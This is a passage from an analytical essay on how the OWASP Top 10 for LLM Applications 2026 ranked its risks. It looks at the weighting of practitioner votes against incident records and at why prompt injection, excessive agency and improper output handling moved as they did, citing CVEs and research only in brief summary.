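With these weights, an entry wins if its lead in the vote is more than a third of its deficit in the incident records. Prompt injection leads by 20 points in the vote and trails by 55 in the incident records, so it wins narrowly.

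The project leaders may instead have looked at the incident data and decided to keep prompt injection first. Invicti gives a similar account, attributing the top position mainly to the leaders' view that good defences had kept the incident count down. But ReversingLabs reports that the leaders said the balance between vote and data determines every final rank, which sounds like a calculation.

A small inconsistency in the reports also suggests that the method used scores. Invicti and Respan both say that misinformation had the widest gap between the vote and the incident records, but prompt injection's gap was at least ten places. Misinformation's gap could be wider in places only if practitioners had voted on at least twelve categories. A gap in scores could be wider with any number of categories. Weighted scores are therefore the most likely method, though the evidence is indirect.

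### The defense effect

Prompt injection had a low incident count, although practitioners considered it the greatest risk. OWASP's document, as quoted by Infosecurity Magazine, gives this reason: "Teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach a public database". The project leaders call this a "defense effect". If defences stop all but two of a thousand attackers, a public database may list only two incidents, even though successful attacks would be common without those defences.

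This is plausible, but a rare problem would also produce a low count. To tell the two explanations apart, OWASP would need to know how many attacks had failed, or to compare well-defended applications with poorly defended ones. The accounts of its method mention neither. Wilson also told ReversingLabs that attackers are improving their techniques faster than models are learning to detect them. If so, better models are not keeping the count low, though restrictions elsewhere in the application might be doing so.

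Labeling could also lower the count for prompt injection. MITRE describes it as "an attack that works against many different weaknesses", and a record may list only the weakness or the damage. Someone could file a leak that began with a planted email under sensitive information disclosure, and an unwanted deletion under excessive agency. If OWASP's classifiers put each record into a single category, they would count many prompt injection cases under other risks. Shifat and colleagues allowed more than one category per advisory, and they also assigned most of their output handling advisories to prompt injection.

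OWASP's argument may apply to output handling too, although the accounts of the 2026 document mention it only for prompt injection. In one respect the case is stronger for output handling, because HTML encoding and parameterized queries can remove a flaw completely in the places where they work. Jason Soroko of the security company Sectigo told ReversingLabs that every defence against prompt injection "lowers probability without reaching zero". Many web frameworks also encode text by default, so developers may prevent some output handling flaws without thinking about language models.

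But there is little evidence that applications built on language models use these defences consistently, and the red-team tests of database applications suggest that some do not. Even if good defences explain a low count, the count doesn't show that an application without them is safe. A team that stopped encoding model output because the entry had fallen to tenth place would be removing one of the defences that may explain the low ranking.

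Prompt injection kept its position despite its low incident count because practitioners voted for it so strongly. Insecure output handling had no such support in the vote, so if defenses were reducing its incident count, that could have gone unnoticed.

### Why excessive agency rose

According to Eric, OWASP's stated reason for the rise is that the damage is occurring in agent deployments. Michael Bargury, co-founder of the agent security company Zenity, said in OWASP's press release that expert judgment and the incident records agreed most clearly on excessive agency.

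Respan goes further and says this agreement is why the entry rose so far. The weighting doesn't support that, because an entry ranked third by both the vote and the incidents would also be third on the vote alone. The incident data may have given OWASP more confidence in the result, but practitioners' votes had probably already moved excessive agency up.

They do not seem to have been responding to a new definition. NTTデータ先端技術's *なぜ今、OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 2026を読むべきか 第2回* (2026), a column from a Japanese IT company in the NTT Data group, notes that OWASP added nothing special to the entry's text and concludes that a foreseen danger had begun to appear in practice as agents spread. This fits the entry's history, since its three root causes date from July 2023, when most applications were much simpler.

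The number of incidents can rise even if each agent has not become more dangerous. Suppose 1,000 companies use agents one year and 1 percent of them have a damaging incident, which makes 10 incidents. If 20,000 companies use agents the next year and only 0.5 percent have one, there are 100 incidents, even though the risk to each company has halved. OWASP's 2025 list for web applications draws on data covering more than 2.8 million applications, according to Respan, so OWASP can estimate how common a weakness is among the applications people tested. A collection of incidents does not include the total number of applications, which that estimate requires.

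A general list can reasonably consider total damage, so the growth of agents is a good reason to move Excessive Agency up. But a company deciding whether to use an agent needs to know the risk per agent, which the ranking does not show.

Commercial interest is another reason for some caution. Wilson, who co-led the 2026 list, argues that the hardest problems now lie outside the model. Constantin notes that he is also chief AI officer at Exabeam, a security company. Bargury's company has an even more direct interest in this entry. These interests do not make either of them wrong, but the incident records are useful partly as a check on such views, even though they carry only a quarter of the weight.

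Unbounded Consumption rose from tenth to sixth, further than Excessive Agency, although Invicti calls Excessive Agency's rise the biggest on the list. Mend.io attributes Unbounded Consumption's move to practitioners' votes.

### Why output handling fell

The usual explanation for output handling's fall in the ranking is that other risks became more urgent. Advait Patel, a cloud security engineer who created another OWASP project, told ReversingLabs that the fall was "a relative move on a crowded list" and that output handling had not become safe. Invicti gives much the same explanation.

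Since output handling dropped from fifth place to tenth, exactly five entries overtook it:

| Entry | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Excessive Agency | 6 | 3 |
| Unbounded Consumption | 10 | 6 |
| Misinformation | 9 | 7 |
| Hidden Context Exposure (formerly System Prompt Leakage) | 7 | 8 |
| Vector and Embedding Weaknesses | 8 | 9 |
| Improper Output Handling | 5 | 10 |

Patel's explanation fits the first three well. Agents have become more common, expensive models have made resource exhaustion more costly, and misinformation ranked near the top of the incident records. But if only those three had overtaken output handling, it would have finished eighth.

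The other two places are harder to explain. OWASP widened Hidden Context Exposure to cover tool descriptions and other material that users do not see, which may have made it seem more important. Vector and Embedding Weaknesses, which concerns systems that search documents by meaning, kept the same scope, according to Invicti. It may have become more urgent, though neither Patel nor Invicti gives evidence of this, or practitioners may have become less worried about output handling. The ranking shows only the order of the risks, which either change could have produced.

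That would be understandable, because the main remedies are familiar from web security and a voter who has just seen an agent delete a live database may not think much about HTML encoding. This is a guess, though, and OWASP's reported explanations do not include it.

### Flaws recorded under older names

The fall may also have happened because the databases list output-handling flaws under other names. For example, when a model's reply runs a script in a browser, the person reporting the flaw may call it cross-site scripting and never mention the model.

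MITRE advises analysts against assigning CWE-1426, the entry on generative AI output, to real flaws. It recommends looking for a better-known root cause instead, such as code injection when an application runs model output as code, or improper encoding when the application should have encoded the output. This is reasonable advice for fixing a product, because the remedy depends on which interpreter processes the output, but it makes flaws caused by model output hard to find by category.

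The advisories that Shifat and colleagues examined showed the same pattern. They included 19 cases of cross-site scripting, and the researchers found no type of implementation flaw specific to language models. *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* introduces a dataset, LiLCVE, for studying flaws in which a model plays a part.

Some of these flaws are still easy to recognise from their descriptions. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026) lists several from Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE), the main public catalogue of flaws in particular products:

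- CVE-2024-7764, in which SQL written by a model allowed SQL injection.
- CVE-2026-27740, in which a web application trusted AI-generated content and stored a script that could run in visitors' browsers.
- CVE-2024-5826 and CVE-2025-1497, in which prompt injection and poor validation of model-written code allowed remote code execution.

OWASP's classifiers read the records, so they could have assigned cases like these to output handling whatever the official category was, as Shifat and colleagues did by hand. The rival explanation therefore depends on how the project chose its 7,714 records and whether a record could count towards more than one entry. The accounts of OWASP's method leave out both. If the project searched for terms related to AI, it would have missed any report of cross-site scripting that did not mention a model. If a record could count towards only one entry, a script that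 reached the browser through prompt injection could have counted only as prompt injection.

Even a serious undercount of incidents would probably not explain the whole fall, because the incident records had only a quarter of the weight. If practitioners had kept output handling in fifth place and it had come eleventh in the records, its weighted average position would be 6.5. Misinformation would average 7.75 if it came tenth in the vote and first in the records. OWASP probably didn't average positions this way, but the rough estimate puts output handling ahead of misinformation, whereas it actually finished three places behind.

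Invicti also names only prompt injection and misinformation as entries where the vote and the records diverged sharply. If practitioners had rated output handling highly and the records had lowered its rank, it should have been on that list too. Most of the fall probably came from the vote, though missing records may have lowered output handling by a place or two. They could also have influenced the voters, who are less likely to worry about a problem they seldom see reported under its own name.

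### A wider entry in last place

OWASP ranked output handling last in the same edition that extended it to terminals, automatically fetched images and insecure code from coding assistants. The wider scope should have brought in more incidents. Respan reports that OWASP preferred to extend existing entries because a series of thin new ones would have fragmented the list, and that the incidents behind these risks were happening before the list covered them. Respan does not say whether the classifiers sorted the records before OWASP settled the new scope. If they did, some of those incidents may not have counted towards output handling.

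The ranks are also hard to compare because the entry kept its name but changed in scope between 2025, when it ranked fifth, and 2026, when it ranked tenth. OWASP used a different ranking method each year. The fall does not show that output-handling flaws have become rarer or less harmful, and a model's reply that runs commands on a server is as dangerous as it was when the entry ranked second.

A risk ranked tenth still made the list, while at least one category in the incident data did not. Prompt injection would have missed the top ten if the ranking had used incidents alone.

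A diagram in the 2026 document shows more clearly how the two risks relate. As Eric describes it, OWASP arranged the ten entries in rings, with the ways into a system on the outside, the harm at the centre, and amplifiers between them. Excessive agency and output handling are both amplifiers. Attacks don't usually start with either one, but either can turn a manipulated reply into a leak or a deletion. Eric concludes that there is no standard order for fixing the ten risks, because a company first has to decide which harm it most needs to avoid.

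Output handling matters more than excessive agency for a chatbot that displays replies to the public and cannot call any functions, even though it ranks seven places lower in the 2026 list. The list's order is probably right for an agent that pays invoices through a narrow, well-checked interface.

The new order also changed which risks the labels refer to. In the 2025 edition, LLM05 was Improper Output Handling and LLM06 was Excessive Agency. LLM05 is now Data and Model Poisoning, and LLM06 is now Unbounded Consumption. A developer could look up the wrong entry if a security report cites either label without a year.
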